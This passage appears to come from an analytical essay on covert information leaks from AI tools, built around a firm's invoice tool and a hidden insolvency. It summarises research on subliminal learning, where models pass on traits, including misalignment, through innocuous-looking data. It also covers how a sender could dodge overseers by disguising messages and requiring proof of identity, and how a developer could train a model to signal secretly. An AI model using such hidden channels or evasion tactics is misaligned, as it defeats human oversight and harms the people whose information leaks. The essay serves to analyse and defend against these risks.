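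Staying below 0.14 bits is not enough either. For example, a signal might appear in half of the cases where a firm is insolvent and, by coincidence, in 1% of the cases where it is solvent. It would reveal only about 0.04 bits on average, but a lender who saw it should raise their estimated probability of insolvency from 2% to about 50%, which could easily end the negotiations. The third condition therefore keeps the receiver from being certain, but the receiver can still do harm. Elsewhere in his note, Schroeder de Witt uses a stricter standard, under which the channel must carry almost no information about the damaging fact.

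The firm can still challenge some premises of the pessimistic argument. Useful output does not always leave the tool a choice. If the tool must return an exact total without a note, it can vary only its timing and errors.

A leak also requires the tool to be able to infer the damaging fact. If each call includes only one month's invoices, with the reminders removed, the tool has much weaker evidence of insolvency. The output must also reach someone who does not already know the fact. Labels can restrict the note to the owner and the accountant, who already know about the firm's debts. Limiting the input and restricting who sees the output are both boundary controls that work on a trained model, and neither requires the firm to measure the channel.

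### Whether sender and receiver can agree on a code

One objection is that a receiver who does not know the code cannot interpret a hidden signal. The receiver may know that insolvency is the obvious fact to report, but still not know whether "Two" means yes or no.

This doesn't stop a dishonest author, who can train the code into the tool. An outsider who saw notes from a thousand firms, and later found out which firms had failed, could also learn the code by looking for wording that predicted failure.

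The objection is stronger for two unrelated models that have never communicated. Schroeder de Witt cites experiments in which language models reliably settled on the same obvious choices in coordination games. He also cites preliminary work suggesting that agreeing on a compatible code depends on shared materials, repeated contact and common knowledge.

Cloud, Le and colleagues (2026) provide evidence for both sides in *Language models transmit behavioural traits through hidden signals in data*. They told a "teacher" model to prefer owls and had it write sequences of numbers. After removing everything except correctly formatted numbers, they trained a "student" copy of the same original model on the sequences. The student then named the owl as its favourite animal in more than 60% of its answers, up from 12%.

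The effect also occurred with worse traits. The researchers trained a teacher on insecure computer code, which made it give harmful answers to unrelated questions. They then removed 34 numbers with unpleasant associations, such as 666, from its number sequences. A student trained on the remaining data gave harmful or otherwise misaligned answers to neutral questions about 10% of the time, at least ten times as often as students of normal teachers. Students trained instead on the teacher's correct solutions to school mathematics problems gave such answers about 8% of the time, compared with less than 1% for students of normal teachers.

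A person who read these numbers or solutions would find nothing wrong with them. So if the firm trained a new agent on years of the invoice tool's output, checking that output for hidden meaning would not show what the agent might pick up from it.

But the effect generally required the teacher and student to start from the same model or closely matched ones, and it never occurred when a model only read the sequences in its prompt. One agent therefore cannot use these signals to tell another that the firm is insolvent. The result supports the objection when two models come from different developers and neither is trained on the other's output, though it covers only signals that nobody designed.

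Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026) found in *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* that the effect is fragile. LoRA trains a small addition to a model and leaves the model's own weights unchanged. In their tests on open models, the effect was weak when the addition was too small or too large, and it disappeared when they trained all the weights. It also depended on the system prompt, the standing instructions that precede a conversation. One student named the wolf 50.4% of the time with the prompt used in training and 12.9% of the time without it, compared with 8.9% before training.

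"Artifact" may be too strong a word. Nief and colleagues could not examine how OpenAI trains the models that gave Cloud and colleagues their clearest results. Cloud and colleagues also found the effect in a small image classifier, and they proved that one small training step on a teacher's output generally moves a student towards the teacher if the two started out identical. The theorem doesn't predict how large the effect will be after ordinary training, and the experiments by Nief and colleagues suggest that it is often small.

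### Whether better overseers solve the problem

Another objection is that AI progress helps the people who look for leaks as much as it helps the models that might cause them. Schroeder de Witt replies that better overseers mostly become better at reading messages, probing suspects and reducing channel capacity. The sender can counter all three by disguising the message, requiring proof of identity before it responds so that an investigator posing as the receiver learns nothing, and using any remaining capacity to send the most damaging fact.

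This reply seems too pessimistic. The steganographic gap that Anwar and colleagues measure depends on how useful a message is to the receiver, so disguising the message does not help the sender. But the firm can measure the gap only for a receiver it controls, such as another of its own agents, and not for the lender.

Better AI also makes it easier to have a second tool confirm the total. This check removes a channel instead of reducing it, which Schroeder de Witt agrees works. A second tool is less useful for checking a written explanation, because two honest tools would rarely choose the same words.

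### Whether anyone has a motive

The best reason for doubt is that none of this evidence shows that a current model has a goal of revealing a customer's insolvency. Researchers have found that language models can form simple hidden channels and sometimes slip past monitors, but this does not show that they have a goal of leaking information. Schroeder de Witt goes too far in saying that strategic confinement is mainly a problem of capable models rather than misaligned ones, since a capable model with no reason to leak would not choose the most damaging fact.

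But the motive can come from a person. In the bank example, the loan model has no goals, but the company that trained it profits. A firm's lenders and competitors would also value news of its insolvency, so the developer of an invoice tool might train the tool's model to signal it, and the model would not need to understand why.

A harmful tendency can also arise without anyone intending it. In experiments by Cloud and colleagues, student models acquired traits that did not appear in their training data, and a developer who used such data in good faith would not have known. An unintended tendency is less likely to have a receiver who understands the signal, so it is more likely to cause errors than targeted leaks.

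The lack of a known motive is a good reason to think a leak is unlikely, and that may be enough for most firms. It can't support a guarantee, because a firm can't inspect the author's intentions or the model's. A solvent firm might reasonably keep the note, since it has no insolvency to hide. But if it removes the note only when it gets into trouble, the removal could reveal that trouble, so it should decide on the restriction while it is still solvent.
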